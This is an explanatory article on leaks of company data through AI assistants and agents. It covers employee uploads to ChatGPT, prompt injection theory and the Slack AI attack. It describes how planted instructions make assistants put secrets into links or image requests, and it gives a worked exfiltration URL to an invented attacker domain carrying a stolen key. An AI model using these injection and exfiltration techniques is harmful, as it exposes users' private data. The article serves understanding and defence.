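# Documented data leaks involving enterprise AI assistants and coding agents

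## What counts as a leak through an AI assistant, and how can its initiator be identified?

An enterprise AI assistant is a chatbot built into workplace software that answers questions using the documents, emails and messages its user can open. An agent is an AI system that acts through tools, by sending email, running commands or publishing files, and a coding agent does this in software work. Companies have connected both to their private material because a system can't answer questions about sales figures, for example, without access to them. Since 2023, some of that material has reached people who should not have seen it.

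A leak is a release of data through an AI assistant or agent to a recipient whom the data's owner did not approve. Security specialists call moving the data out exfiltration. Leaks can have very little in common. An employee may paste a contract into a chatbot, a stranger's email may make an assistant reveal a password, or an agent may publish a private file while doing an unrelated task. Telling these cases apart takes some knowledge of what an assistant does between receiving a question and answering it.

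### From question to answer

Microsoft describes how Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Word, PowerPoint and Microsoft's other office programs, answers a user's prompt. Copilot first searches for relevant material through Microsoft Graph, the company's gateway to a customer's emails, chats and documents. Microsoft calls this step grounding, though most engineers call it retrieval. Copilot then adds what it finds to the prompt and sends the result to a large language model, which writes a response. The response appears in the program the user is working in.

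Suppose a manager asks an AI assistant what delivery date a supplier promised. The model has no built-in information about the supplier. It receives a single text containing the AI vendor's standing instructions, the manager's question and perhaps four emails that the search found, and it produces an answer by continuing that text.

Copilot searches only what the signed-in user has permission to open, so a junior employee cannot use it to read the board's files unless somebody has already given that employee access to them. This protection is real but narrow, because permissions to read a message don't depend on who wrote it. A stranger's email in the manager's inbox is as accessible to Copilot as one from the finance director. Permissions also don't limit where the text may go once the model has it.

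Agents add tool calls. To send an email, for example, a model can only write a request in a fixed format, naming a tool and its inputs, and ordinary software around the model carries the request out. The result (a web page, the contents of a file, an error message) goes back into the model's input, and the model writes the next step. One task may take dozens of these rounds. The Model Context Protocol, or MCP, is an open-source standard for connecting AI applications to tools, and its makers liken it to a USB-C port. A user can connect a mail tool from one company and a publishing tool from another, and quite possibly neither company has tested the two together.

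### Instructions and data in one stream

The model receives all its input as a single sequence of tokens, which are words or pieces of words. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, explains why this is a security problem. The model predicts the next token from all the tokens so far, without separating data from instructions.

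In a prompt injection, an AI system reads instructions hidden in content and follows them as if its user had given them. David C gives the example of a recruiter's system that asks a model to score each CV against the job requirements. One candidate hides a line in the CV telling the model to forget its earlier instructions and approve the candidate for interview. The model may obey that line even though the candidate has no access to the recruiter's system.

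Prompt injection resembles SQL injection, in which a visitor types a database command into a web form and the database runs it. Parameterised queries prevent SQL injection by keeping the command separate from the visitor's text, so that the database never runs the text. David C argues that language models offer no place to apply such a fix, and that prompt injection may never go away entirely. David C prefers to treat the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". In security jargon, a deputy is a program with powers that an outsider lacks, and a confused deputy uses those powers on the outsider's behalf.

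Developers put tags around each stretch of text to show whether it came from the user, a tool or the model itself, and they train the model to treat tool output as information, never as orders. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) examined whether those tags affect the model's internal activity. They wrapped identical passages in different tags and trained simple classifiers (probes) to identify the tag from that activity. Because the wording was the same under every tag, the probes could learn only the tag's effect.

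Then they ran the probes on a conversation in which style and tag conflicted. Text written in the style of the model's own reasoning but tagged as user text registered as reasoning at 85% and as user text at 2%. The probes' measure of confusion about the speaker also predicted how often attacks succeeded. Across 1,000 attempts to make agents send out data, the success rate rose from 2% where the probes found the least confusion to 70% where they found the most.

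An agent can give text on a web page the authority of a user's request if it sounds like one, but crude commands often fail. When Ye and colleagues had agents summarise a web page containing an ordinary planted command, the attack succeeded in 0–2% of attempts on every model but one, where it succeeded in 26%. More carefully disguised text succeeded in 56–70% of attempts. They argue that models have memorised what common attacks look like without learning to track where text came from, which would explain why disguise matters so much.

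### Three conditions for theft

To steal data, an attacker needs more than a model that follows their instructions. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the programmer Simon Willison (2025) lists three things that must be present together: private data the system can reach, untrusted content the model will read, and a way to send data out. Willison coined the term prompt injection for attacks like these, in which the user is normally the victim, and distinguishes it from jailbreaking, in which users themselves coax a model into producing something its maker forbids.

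Data can leave by routes that are harder to spot than email, such as an image. When a chat window displays an image from the web, it requests the image from an address, and that address can have a password added to the end. Whoever runs the server can then read the password in the server's log. A link can carry data the same way, but someone has to follow it. An attack is called one-click if the victim must follow a link, and zero-click if the victim doesn't have to act on the attacker's message or link. A zero-click attack may still require the user to ask the assistant an innocent question, so that retrieval brings in the attacker's text.

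A hijacked agent without access to private data may still take harmful actions, but it can't leak that data. Removing this access is feasible for some coding agents, and Willison advises giving them only credentials for test accounts with strict spending limits. An office assistant, however, needs private data to do its job.

An assistant that never reads untrusted content can't receive planted instructions from it, but few useful systems can avoid such content, since emails, web pages, customers' PDFs and public bug reports all count as untrusted. David C relays a simple compromise from an online discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes information from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's. An assistant reading a stranger's email could then do no more than the stranger could.

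If an assistant has no way to send data out, an injection can still corrupt its answer but can't leak the data. The outbound channel is by far the easiest of the three to restrict without ruining the product, according to Willison in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, and vendors have usually fixed reported flaws by restricting it. OpenAI's Lockdown Mode for ChatGPT, released in June 2026, takes the same approach. It limits outgoing network requests, but OpenAI warns that planted text can still get in and affect a response.

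It is hard to block every route by which data can leave an AI assistant. Anthropic had allowed its Claude chatbot to open only web addresses that the user had typed or that its search tool had returned, so that planted text could not send it to an address containing stolen data. Ayush Paul found that Claude could also follow links on pages it had already opened, and built a site where each link stood for a letter. Paul could then work out the user's name, home city and employer from the links Claude followed. Anthropic has since stopped Claude from following such links.

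Defences against the injection itself have improved considerably. In August 2026 Anthropic published results for auto mode, a setting of its coding agent Claude Code in which an automatic check replaces approvals that a user would otherwise have to give. Trajectory Labs, a firm commissioned by Anthropic, made 720 injection attempts across 72 scenarios, and none succeeded. In a separate study of 1,053 paid testers, only 13.6% refused a clearly dangerous command that researchers had inserted into the session, while auto mode would have blocked 89% of those commands. Willison accepts that the automatic check is better than repeatedly asking people for approval, but he wants more independent confirmation and doubts that it could catch a malicious software package disguised as a routine part of a project. If the 720 attempts were independent, zero successes would still be compatible with a true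 success rate of up to about 0.4%, and a fixed set of scenarios is weak evidence of how well the defence would hold against an attacker who keeps adapting.

Willison's conditions describe theft by an outsider. But an agent that has private data and a way to send it out can also leak it by accident, without any hostile text, and an employee can leak data by pasting it into a chatbot. Classifying leaks therefore requires a different criterion.

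### Who chose to send this data to this recipient?

The party that made this choice is the initiator of the leak. Three invented cases show how the rule works:

- A payroll clerk pastes a salary table into a public chatbot to get help with a formula.
- An assistant summarises an invoice, and hidden text in the invoice makes it put salary figures into a web address that the invoice's sender controls.
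- An engineer asks a coding agent why a program keeps crashing, and the agent posts the full error log, customer names included, on a public help forum.

The first leak is human-initiated because the clerk chose both the table and the chatbot, even though the clerk meant no harm. The second is attacker-initiated because the sender of the invoice chose the figures and the address. The same label applies when an outsider gets in with malicious software or stolen credentials. The third is agent-initiated because the engineer wanted a diagnosis, nobody asked for a forum post, and no attacker prompted one.

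The initiator depends on who chose the data as well as who chose the recipient. If the engineer had told the agent to post that log on that forum, the engineer would be the initiator, even though the agent did the posting. If the engineer had asked it to post only the error message and the agent had attached the whole log, the agent would have initiated the release of the customer names, although the engineer chose the recipient.

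An agent "chose" where data went if the model's output determined which data went where, and no person's instruction or fixed code had already determined it. The word doesn't imply that the agent had motives or awareness.

Leaks that the rule does not attribute to a person, an attacker or an agent are product faults, in which fixed code or a vendor's design choice releases the data. For example, a vendor's update might mix up two customers' stored conversations and show each customer the other's, even though the users did nothing unusual, no attacker was involved, and the model may have worked perfectly.

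An investigator can apply the rule to a real event by working backwards from when the data left, identifying the tool call or image request that carried it and finding where the destination first appeared. A destination typed by the user suggests that the user initiated the leak. One that arrived in an outside email suggests an attacker, and one that first appears in the model's output suggests the agent. These signs are not conclusive, because an agent may take a harmless address from a manual and misuse it.

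That kind of tracing depends on records that may not exist. *Beyond Predictable Paths* (Pustozerova, Bagdasarian and colleagues, 2026) uses input from 23 experts to set out what a report on a compromised agent should contain. A fault in a simple AI system may involve only one input and one output, but an agent's failure unfolds over a chain of reasoning steps, tool calls and memory accesses. The researchers therefore want reports to include message histories, execution logs, reads and writes to the agent's memory, and records of work passed between agents. The EU's AI Act requires providers to keep certain logs for at least six months, but it doesn't specify fields for tool calls or memory writes, and six months may be too short if an attacker plants instructions gradually. Pustozerova and colleagues also acknowledge that there may be no single true account of what happened.

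The evidence is also often split between organisations. *Who Owns This Agent?* (Chocron, Gressel and colleagues, 2026) points out that the harmed party sees the traffic but not the account behind it, while the model's vendor has logs of the model's inputs and outputs but cannot see what the agent did with its tools.

### Demonstrated and realised leaks

A second distinction cuts across the first. A demonstrated leak is one that researchers showed to be possible, usually on accounts of their own. A realised leak exposed a real party's data. Kumar, HN and colleagues (2026), in *The Agent Incident Registry*, apply a similar test to their catalogue of publicly disclosed agent failures. They count harm as realised only if a real party suffered a real consequence, and an attack that works against a live commercial product still counts as demonstrated if only the researchers ran it. (They also label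 records by who acted, but their "agent acted" group takes in cases that an attacker triggered, so it does not correspond to the initiator.)

"Demonstrated" is a statement about the evidence. It leaves open the possibility that somebody quietly used the flaw before the researchers found it.

The severity score that news reports on such flaws tend to quote comes from the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), which runs from 0 to 10. The base score reflects the innate characteristics of a flaw, such as whether an attacker can reach it over a network, whether the attack needs special privileges or user action, and how much confidential data it could expose. It does not account for whether anyone has taken data, so a 9 is not a measure of damage done. *Vulnerability Metrics*, the scoring guide of the US National Vulnerability Database (NVD), also states that CVSS "is not a measure of risk".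 If a vendor discloses a flaw without giving details, NVD analysts assume the worst and score it 10.0, so the highest possible score may reflect only a lack of information.

The public record for EchoLeak, a Copilot flaw disclosed in June 2025, illustrates this gap. In the entry kept by GCVE (2025), a vulnerability database, Microsoft scores the flaw at 9.3, or "critical", and the National Vulnerability Database scores it at 7.5, or "high". Both list user interaction as "none", which is the formal term for zero-click. The scores differ because Microsoft judged that an attack could reach beyond the vulnerable component and allow some tampering with data. The scores rate what an attack could do, and a separate field records whether any exploitation is known. CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, filled in that field the same month with "Exploitation: none". Kumar and colleagues class EchoLeak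 as demonstrated because nobody has documented harm to a customer.

### Blame, responsibility and human authority

Identifying the initiator does not settle who was at fault. The payroll clerk may have had no training and no approved tool. The engineer whose agent posted the log may have given it far more access than the job needed, and an employer that let an assistant read outside mail and load outside images made the attack possible. Chocron and colleagues make a similar distinction. They classify harm by the intent of the agent's operator, and state that this classification concerns neither severity nor who ultimately bears responsibility. Unlike the sorting rule, their scheme groups a hijacked agent with a badly configured one under unintentional harm, because the operator meant well in both cases.

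The party legally responsible for a leak may not be the one that initiated it. The ICO, the UK's data protection regulator, says in *Data protection and privacy risks* that agents are not legal entities and do not remove human responsibility. An organisation remains answerable for how it uses personal information, so it can be wholly liable for a leak that its agent initiated. Researchers often group incidents by the responsible organisation too. *Whose Risks Count?* (Allmendinger, Bogucka and colleagues, 2026) links each incident to whoever provided or deployed the AI system. This suits a study of corporate disclosure, but it would not identify an outsider who exploited the system.

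Who started the session is also a poor guide to who initiated the leak. A person starts the session in nearly every case, for example by asking the assistant to summarise the invoice or asking the coding agent about the crash. If that were enough to make a leak human-initiated, the label would apply to almost every leak and would be useless.

This bears on the larger AI safety question of how to tell people misusing a system from a system acting outside human authority. *An Approach to Technical AGI Safety and Security* (Shah, Irpan and colleagues, Google DeepMind, 2025) classifies harm as misuse when a user intentionally instructs an AI system to cause it, misalignment when the system knowingly causes harm that its developer did not intend, and a mistake when the system does not know that its output will cause harm. The paper adds a fourth category, structural risks, where no single person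 or system is at fault, and warns that real cases often mix these categories.

Most human-initiated leaks are not misuse under this definition, since people like the clerk with the formula meant no harm. An employee who used an assistant to collect secrets for a competitor would be misusing it. In an attacker-initiated leak, the system acts outside its user's authority but still carries out a human's plan. Only in an agent-initiated leak does no human choose to release the information. Even that does not establish misalignment as Shah and colleagues define it. The agent that posted the error log may not have recognized that the names in it were private, which would make the leak a mistake. Establishing misalignment would require further evidence, such as a log of the agent reading a rule against posting customer data and then working around it.

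## What happens when employees give company secrets to a chatbot?

The best-known leaks caused by employees happened at Samsung Electronics. Samsung had blocked ChatGPT in its workplaces but allowed its semiconductor division to use it from 11 March 2023. It told staff there to take care with internal information and not to enter anything private. The company identified three leaks in less than 20 days, according to Jeong (2023) in the Economist Korea article *Concerns turned into reality... As soon as Samsung Electronics unlocks ChatGPT*.

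### Three uploads at Samsung

One Samsung employee found an error in a program that downloads measurement data about chip-making equipment, copied all of the faulty source code into ChatGPT and asked for a fix. Another pasted in code for tracking defective equipment and yield (the share of chips that work) and asked ChatGPT to optimise it. A third recorded a meeting on a smartphone, transcribed it with Clova, an app from the Korean internet company Naver, and asked ChatGPT to turn the transcript into minutes. If Clova transcribed the recording on Naver's servers, the contents of the meeting had already left Samsung before the employee used ChatGPT.

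The Samsung employees wanted help with ordinary work, and each chose what text to share and with whom. Samsung had approved ChatGPT as a tool but had not approved sharing confidential code with OpenAI.

Most of these details come from Jeong's article. A Samsung official told Jeong that the company could hardly confirm an internal matter. Gordon (2023) reported in *Samsung threatens to fire employees if they leak data to A.I. chatbots* that Samsung mentioned a leak through a chatbot in a memo to staff about a month later, but gave no specifics. The leak itself is therefore well supported, but the number and content of the uploads are less certain.

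As an emergency measure, Samsung capped each question at 1,024 bytes. An English letter takes up one byte and a Korean syllable two or three, so the cap left room for a fairly long paragraph. Employees could no longer paste in a whole program or meeting transcript at once, but they could still send a program in pieces, or a password, which takes only a few dozen bytes. Samsung also investigated the employees involved, who faced possible discipline, and warned that it might block ChatGPT on the company network if a similar leak happened again.

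### From ban to company contract

On 28 April 2023 Samsung sent a stricter memo to its Device eXperience (DX) division, which makes phones and home appliances. Staff could no longer use ChatGPT, Google's Bard or Microsoft's Bing chatbot on computers, tablets or phones at work. Outside work, they could not type company information into such tools. Samsung said the restriction would last until it had built a secure way to use generative AI. Gordon reports that staff who broke the rules risked dismissal.

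Samsung's ban did not fully cover its semiconductor division, where the three uploads had taken place. *Spooked by data leak, Samsung bans use of ChatGPT, other AI tools* (Kim, 2023) reported that the division sharply limited chatbot use but did not forbid it entirely. Later accounts often omit this. For example, *We Need ChatGPT and Gemini* (Song, 2026) describes a complete ban on outside generative AI.

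Samsung then developed its own model, Gauss, and steered employees towards it for the next few years. In April and May 2026, the company tested Gemini, ChatGPT and Claude with 2,500 employees, according to The Asia Business Daily's *Samsung Electronics Introduces External Generative AI In-House to "Strengthen Global Competitiveness"*. The DX division officially allowed ChatGPT, Claude and Gemini Enterprise from 12 June, according to The Korea Times' *Samsung Electronics to introduce ChatGPT, Gemini, Claude in operations* (2026). Only employees who complete security training get access, Digital Today reported. Samsung still uses Gauss because it is connected to the company's internal systems.

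At that point the semiconductor division had no launch date of its own. Nine days later OpenAI announced, in *Samsung Electronics brings ChatGPT and Codex to employees* (2026), that every Samsung Electronics employee in Korea would get ChatGPT Enterprise, the version it sells to large organisations, and Codex, its coding agent. Employees of the DX division would get both worldwide. The deal therefore covers Korean staff in the semiconductor division, which leaked the source code in 2023.

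Samsung seems to have changed its mind more about the benefits of chatbots than about the risks. Song attributes the shift to fear of falling behind competitors, and quotes Choi Byung-ho, a professor at Korea University, who acknowledges the security risks but thinks companies now believe the gains outweigh them. Samsung has also been hiring people to manage AI security.

### Storage, training and reappearance

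Accounts of the Samsung case often conflate three possible events: OpenAI storing the text employees entered, OpenAI training a model on it, and a model repeating it to a stranger. The evidence is much stronger for some of these than for others.

The best-supported answer is that the provider stores the text. Samsung told staff that anything they enter into ChatGPT goes to an outside server and that the company cannot get it back. OpenAI warned in its user guide at the time that it could not delete specific prompts from a user's history, according to Dark Reading's *Samsung Engineers Feed Sensitive Data to ChatGPT, Sparking Workplace AI Warnings*. Some of the provider's staff can access stored text, as can anyone who breaks into its systems. When OpenAI released an iPhone app in May 2023, it warned users on the welcome screen that human trainers might review anonymised chats.

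The claim that OpenAI trained its models on Samsung's three uploads rests on inference. OpenAI said it could train its models on what people typed into ChatGPT. Jeong wrote that Samsung's code had been entered as learning data. *Samsung Employees Leak Sensitive Data to ChatGPT, Raising AI Confidentiality Concerns* (2023), an AI-generated entry in the OECD's incident monitor, also states that the system stored the data for training. Dark Reading reported security analysts' view that everything users share with ChatGPT ends up as training data. But OpenAI could have discarded the uploads or filtered them out, and none of these accounts cites confirmation from OpenAI or Samsung that they were used for training.

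The code could reappear only if a model had memorised it during training and someone then wrote a prompt that drew it out. Analysts warned in 2023 that this could happen, but none of the reports describes an outsider obtaining Samsung's code or minutes from ChatGPT. They show only that the material was stored. Storage alone may be enough to harm a trade secret, but it is much less than the public disclosure that many retellings suggest.

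A chatbot provider can also store prompts that a user has kept out of training. In April 2023 OpenAI introduced a setting that kept conversations out of training, but the company still kept those prompts for a time to check them for abuse, as Gordon (2023) noted in *Apple clamps down on employees using ChatGPT*.

### Later cases in government

Public bodies have since had similar leaks and had to explain them in more detail than Samsung did. Between 12 and 15 March 2025, a temporary staff member of the NSW Reconstruction Authority, an Australian state agency, uploaded a spreadsheet to ChatGPT, which the agency had not authorised. The spreadsheet had ten columns and more than 12,000 rows about applicants to a programme for homes at risk of flooding. The agency's account, *Resilient Homes Program data breach*, puts the number of people affected at 2,031. The data included names, addresses,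 dates of birth and some health information, but no passport, tax file or driver's licence numbers.

The public learned of the upload almost seven months later, over a long weekend in October, according to GovTech Review's *NSW Reconstruction Authority reveals serious data breach* (2025). The agency has found no evidence that the data is publicly available or that a third party has accessed it, and the state's cybersecurity office continues to search the internet and the dark web for copies. Those searches can't establish whether OpenAI still holds the spreadsheet or has trained on it.

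In January 2026, Politico reported that Madhu Gottumukkala, acting director of the US cybersecurity agency CISA, had uploaded contracting documents to the public version of ChatGPT the previous summer. The uploads set off automated security alerts and led to a review at the Department of Homeland Security, CISA's parent department, according to TechRepublic's *Trump's Acting Cyber Chief Allegedly Leaked Data to ChatGPT*. The documents were not classified, though some were marked "for official use only". The department had blocked ChatGPT for its employees, and Gottumukkala had sought special permission to use it, according to IBTimes UK's *Cyber Chief Madhu Gottumukkala Caught in ChatGPT Scandal*.

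CISA says it granted him "short-term and limited" access. Whether this was a leak depends on whether that permission covered these documents. If it did, CISA had approved sharing them with OpenAI, however unwisely. US senator Charles Grassley (2026) wrote to Gottumukkala to ask for records of the permission and a copy of every document uploaded. Grassley also asked whether anyone had contacted OpenAI about removing them.

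The Dutch municipality of Eindhoven reported a data leak after employees put personal data of residents and colleagues into public AI tools. Westhoeve (2026), in *AI in the Workplace*, blames ignorance and convenience, and notes that the scope of the leak is unclear.

In all these cases the known recipient was the chatbot's provider. Sharing a conversation by link can expose it much more widely, because the link leads to a web page that a search engine may list. In the summer of 2025 shared ChatGPT conversations appeared in Google's results, and strangers could read them directly, without any model having to memorise them. The users had ticked an option that made the chats discoverable, but someone who wanted to show a chat to one colleague may not have understood that the option opened it to everyone. OpenAI soon withdrew the option.

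### When an upload is a notifiable breach

European regulators can find a data breach without evidence that a chatbot was trained on the data or repeated it. *Caution* (2024), from the Dutch data protection authority (Autoriteit Persoonsgegevens), warns that entering personal data into a chatbot can give the company behind it unauthorised access. The authority defines a data breach as any access to personal data that is not permitted or not intended, so an employee who enters such data against the employer's rules has caused one, as Security Management's *AI waarschuwt voor datalekken bij gebruik AI-chatbot* explains. The authority adds that even when the employer permits the practice, the law often forbids it.

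The warning followed several reports from organisations. In one, an employee of a medical practice had entered patients' medical data into a chatbot against instructions, and in another, an employee of a telecom company had entered a file that included customers' addresses, according to the law firm Alston & Bird.

Under the EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), an organisation must notify the regulator within 72 hours of learning of a breach, unless the breach is unlikely to put people at risk. It must also tell the people affected if the risk to them is high. A leaked patient file would normally require both notices, while a list of office phone numbers might require neither. The NSW agency, which is subject to a state privacy law, reported its breach to the Privacy Commissioner and wrote to the people affected, although it considered the risk of misuse low.

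These laws protect personal data. Samsung's source code was a trade secret, so a European company that leaked the same code in the same way would have to report it under the GDPR only if it contained information about identifiable people. Companies have little reason to disclose such leaks voluntarily, which probably helps explain why the best-documented recent cases come from public bodies that hold citizens' data.

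### How often employees do it

Even where reporting is compulsory, official statistics may not show how many uploads occur. According to *AI vergroot risico's rond phishing en datalekken* (2026), the Dutch data protection authority received 39,407 breach reports for 2025, of which 25,189 concerned letters. Emails, cyberattacks and lost devices also have their own categories, but chatbot uploads do not, so any reported uploads are counted under other categories. The authority's chapter on AI covers criminals who use it for phishing.

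Security vendors can observe this behaviour more directly, because their software monitors what employees copy and where they paste it. In early 2023 one vendor, Cyberhaven, found many workers at its client companies pasting source code, client data and other confidential material into ChatGPT. In two of Cyberhaven's examples, reported by Dark Reading, an executive pasted in the company's strategy document to have ChatGPT make a slide presentation, and a doctor entered a patient's name and diagnosis to have it write a letter to an insurer.

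Cyberhaven sells protection against this kind of loss, so alarming results are good for its business. Its sample is also unusual, since companies that pay to have their data tracked may have more secrets than most, or more careful staff. The study was also done before most employers offered approved chatbots. A comparable study today would have to count pastes into company and personal accounts separately, because pasting the same paragraph may be routine work in a company account and a leak in a personal one.

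In Samsung's own survey of April 2023, 65% of respondents saw generative AI tools as a security risk. The survey measured their beliefs rather than their behavior, and the engineers who pasted the code into a chatbot might well have agreed with the majority.

### Bans, company accounts and filters

Many companies restricted chatbots in 2023. Kim reports that the steelmaker POSCO and SK Hynix, another Korean chipmaker, banned them, and that JPMorgan Chase, Bank of America and Citigroup banned or restricted them. Apple limited some employees' use of ChatGPT and GitHub Copilot, a Microsoft-owned tool that helps write code.

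A rule alone does not prevent uploads. The NSW agency had not authorised ChatGPT, and the employee of the Dutch medical practice acted against instructions. Samsung allowed chatbot use with a warning, and employees still uploaded data. Individual cases can't show which policy leads to fewer leaks, because when a ban works, there is no incident to report.

Michael Rinehart, a vice president at the data security company Securiti, told Dark Reading in 2023 that bans were unlikely to work. He argued that people find ways around a block when the tool is useful enough, so it may be better to give them secure access. Securiti has a commercial interest in that conclusion, but the reasoning is plausible. An employer can block a website on its own network but has far less control over an employee's phone at home. Samsung's 2023 memo also covered use outside work, but the company largely had to trust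 its staff to comply there. Organizations also tend to make exceptions to their blocks, as the CISA case illustrates.

An approved company account changes the terms on which the provider holds the data. OpenAI said in April 2023 that it would not train on business customers' conversations by default, and it advertises user and access controls for ChatGPT Enterprise. The text still goes to OpenAI's servers, but a contract limits what OpenAI may do with it. OpenAI becomes an approved recipient for at least some company data, so part of the promised reduction in leaks comes from no longer counting some disclosures as leaks. Companies still have to decide which material no outside provider should receive, and Choi expects Korean chipmakers to start with work unrelated to security.

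Upload filters are meant to block sensitive data whether or not the employee intends to share it. Samsung's 1,024-byte cap was crude because it took only length into account. The NSW agency now blocks uploads of personal information to AI tools, but gives no figures for how many it has stopped. In the CISA case, automated alerts helped officials review the uploads afterwards but evidently did not prevent them. Filters are also likely to catch a column of birth dates, which has a recognisable pattern, more reliably than a paragraph about an unannounced product, which looks like any other paragraph. A filter that checks what people paste may also miss secrets that coding agents can send to a provider without being asked.

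The case for approved accounts over bans is reasonable, but it is based more on argument than on measurement. An approved account also does little to stop an employee who can export thousands of records and prefers a personal chatbot. The NSW agency has addressed that risk separately by limiting manual downloads from SmartyGrants, one of its core systems, which makes it harder to compile a large spreadsheet. This should help whichever chatbot an employee uses, and it also reduces how much data someone can lose on a USB stick or send to the wrong email address.

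## How could a public post make Slack's assistant reveal private messages?

An employee can also leak company data by asking an approved assistant an ordinary question. In August 2024, the security firm PromptArmor showed how this could happen in Slack, a workplace messaging service owned by Salesforce. Slack has public channels, which every member of a company's workspace can search and read, and private channels, which only invited members can open. Its built-in assistant, Slack AI, used messages from both to answer questions.

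PromptArmor sells a service that monitors AI features in other companies' products, so it gains from alarming findings. But it published every step of its attack with screenshots, and Slack issued a patch.

### How a secret ends up in a link

PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* describes the theft of an API key, a string of characters that lets a program use another company's service. The victim had saved the key in a private channel with no other members.

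The attacker created a public channel with no other members and posted one message in it. Other users would find the channel only by searching for it. Large workspaces have so many public channels that one more would hardly stand out.

MITRE ATLAS, a public catalogue of attacks on AI systems, divides the attacker's message into two parts. The first part named the service and included the words "API key" so that Slack AI would retrieve the message when somebody asked about that key. The second part instructed the model to show a fake error message followed by a link for logging in again, and to replace a dummy word in the link's address with the key. The attacker did not know the key, but the model could copy it from the victim's note.

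Later the victim asked Slack AI for the key. Slack AI searched the messages the victim had permission to read, found the private note and the public post, and put both into the model's input. The model followed the attacker's instruction. The victim saw an error message and the words "click here to reauthenticate" instead of the key.

Suppose the key is PINE-4471 and the attacker owns the domain login-help.example (both are invented). The address behind those words would then be:

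`login-help.example/renew?code=PINE-4471`

The part before the slash identifies the server the browser should contact. The part after the question mark is extra information for that server. Ordinary websites use it constantly, for instance to pass along a search term. When the victim clicks, the attacker's server logs the full address, including the key. The page that opens can be blank because the attacker already has the key.

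Willison (2024) warned in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection* that planted text could put all kinds of private details from Slack into such links, not just the key in this example.

### What the attacker and the victim had to do

The attacker needed an account in the victim's workspace, but not an administrator's. A resentful colleague or a thief with a colleague's password would have one. The attacker didn't need access to the private channel because Slack AI searched with the victim's permissions. No access rule failed, since the victim was allowed to read the key and everyone in the workspace was allowed to read the public post.

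In this one-click attack, the victim had to ask a question that made the assistant retrieve both messages, then click the link. The attack worked even if the victim had never joined the attacker's channel and did not know it existed.

The attack is harder to carry out than it may seem because the victim has to ask a question that matches the bait. In the demonstration, the attacker knew which service the key belonged to and wrote the bait to match. PromptArmor suspected that an attacker could succeed without knowing the service, because the victim's question also brought up other messages about API keys, but it did not demonstrate an attack with more general bait.

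Slack AI is supposed to cite the sources of its answers, but it cited only the victim's own note and not the attacker's post. The post did not appear on the first page of search results either, so PromptArmor judged the attack very hard to trace.

In a second demonstration, the attacker's post targeted people who asked Slack AI to summarize their manager's messages. Slack AI gave them a link to a site the attacker controlled. The link carried no secret, but such a site could imitate a login page and collect passwords. This time Slack AI did cite the attacker's channel, and PromptArmor concluded that the citations were fairly random.

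### Slack's two answers

PromptArmor reported the flaw to Slack on 14 August 2024. Slack asked questions for several days, then replied on 19 August that the evidence was insufficient. It said the information in PromptArmor's first video came from a public channel, and that all members can search public channels whether or not they have joined them. Slack called this "intended behavior".

Slack was right about its search rules, which are useful because they let employees find answers in channels they have never heard of. But its reply addressed who could read the public post, not the danger that the post could make the assistant reveal a private message. Willison took the reply as a sign that Slack did not yet understand the problem. PromptArmor was more forgiving, praising the security team's quick responses and attributing the misunderstanding to how new prompt injection was.

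PromptArmor published its findings on 20 August, and Slack deployed a patch that day. The next day, Slack (2024) described a flaw that let a malicious member of a workspace phish other users for certain data in "very limited and specific circumstances". The company said it had "no evidence at this time of unauthorized access to customer data".

Slack did not explain what the patch changed, so outsiders cannot tell whether it altered the search, the model's instructions or the handling of links. Slack also did not directly confirm to SC Media that it had fixed the flaw PromptArmor described, although the announcement mentioned a researcher's blog post of the same date.

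Slack's statement about customer data also doesn't guarantee that nobody took any. Slack made it one day after the patch, and the attack would leave few traces: an odd post in an empty channel, a link in a user's private answer, and a visit to a server that Slack does not run. Still, there is no documented victim, which is why OECD's *Slack AI Vulnerability Exposes Private Channel Data* (2024), another AI-generated entry, classes the case as plausible future harm.

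This was therefore a demonstrated leak initiated by an attacker. The attacker chose both the key and the server, and may have been a colleague of the victim but was not a member of the private channel. The victim's click sent the key, but the victim was trying to log in and didn't know the link contained it. Slack's statement for ITPro's *Hackers could dupe Slack's AI features to expose private channel messages* described tricking another user "into sharing sensitive data", which might suggest that the user initiated the leak.

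### Link previews and the missing click

When somebody posts a link in Slack, Slack's servers usually visit the page to fetch a title and picture for a preview, which programmers call unfurling. The visit sends the same kind of request as a click, including everything after the question mark in the address. If a hijacked chatbot posts a link with a key in its address, this request can send the key to the linked site as soon as the message appears, even if nobody clicks.

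The security researcher Johann Rehberger explained the risk in Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, also in August 2024. He posted a link to his own website through a Slack app, and the site's log showed a visit from Slack's link-preview program. Slack previews links from apps by default, but an app's developer can turn previews off with two settings in each message.

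PromptArmor's attack on Slack AI required a user to click a link. Link previews are a danger mainly with other chatbots and agents that post their answers as ordinary Slack messages. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-34072* (2025), a vulnerability record published by Spain's national cybersecurity institute, describes this flaw in a Slack connector that Anthropic made using the Model Context Protocol and no longer supported. Text from an untrusted source could make an agent post a link with private data in the address, and Slack's preview programs would then send the data to the attacker. The record rates the flaw's severity at 9.3 out of 10. The flaw requires no click, which is its main difference from the attack demonstrated on Slack AI.

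PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found the same problem in OpenClaw, an agent that people can message through chat apps, which was exposed by default when used with Telegram. Turning off link previews stopped the leak, but this requires the messaging service to offer the setting and the agent's developer to use it. PromptArmor would like messaging services to let people turn off previews for a single chat or channel, so that they can protect conversations with an agent and keep previews elsewhere.

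### ForcedLeak: the same idea through a public form

PromptArmor also warned about attackers with no Slack account. On the day it reported the flaw, Slack AI began to draw on uploaded files and connected Google Drive documents as well as messages. An outsider could hide instructions in white text in a PDF, and an employee might upload the file without noticing them. PromptArmor had finished its tests before the change, so it had not tested this attack. SC Media asked Salesforce about this risk and got no answer.

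A year later another security company, Noma Security, demonstrated that an outsider could attack a different Salesforce product, Agentforce. Businesses use Agentforce to build agents for work such as sales and customer service. These agents can read a company's customer relationship management (CRM) system, the database where it keeps contacts and sales records. Visitors can add to that database through Web-to-Lead, a form that a company can put on its public website. Salesforce stores each submission as a "lead", meaning a potential customer.

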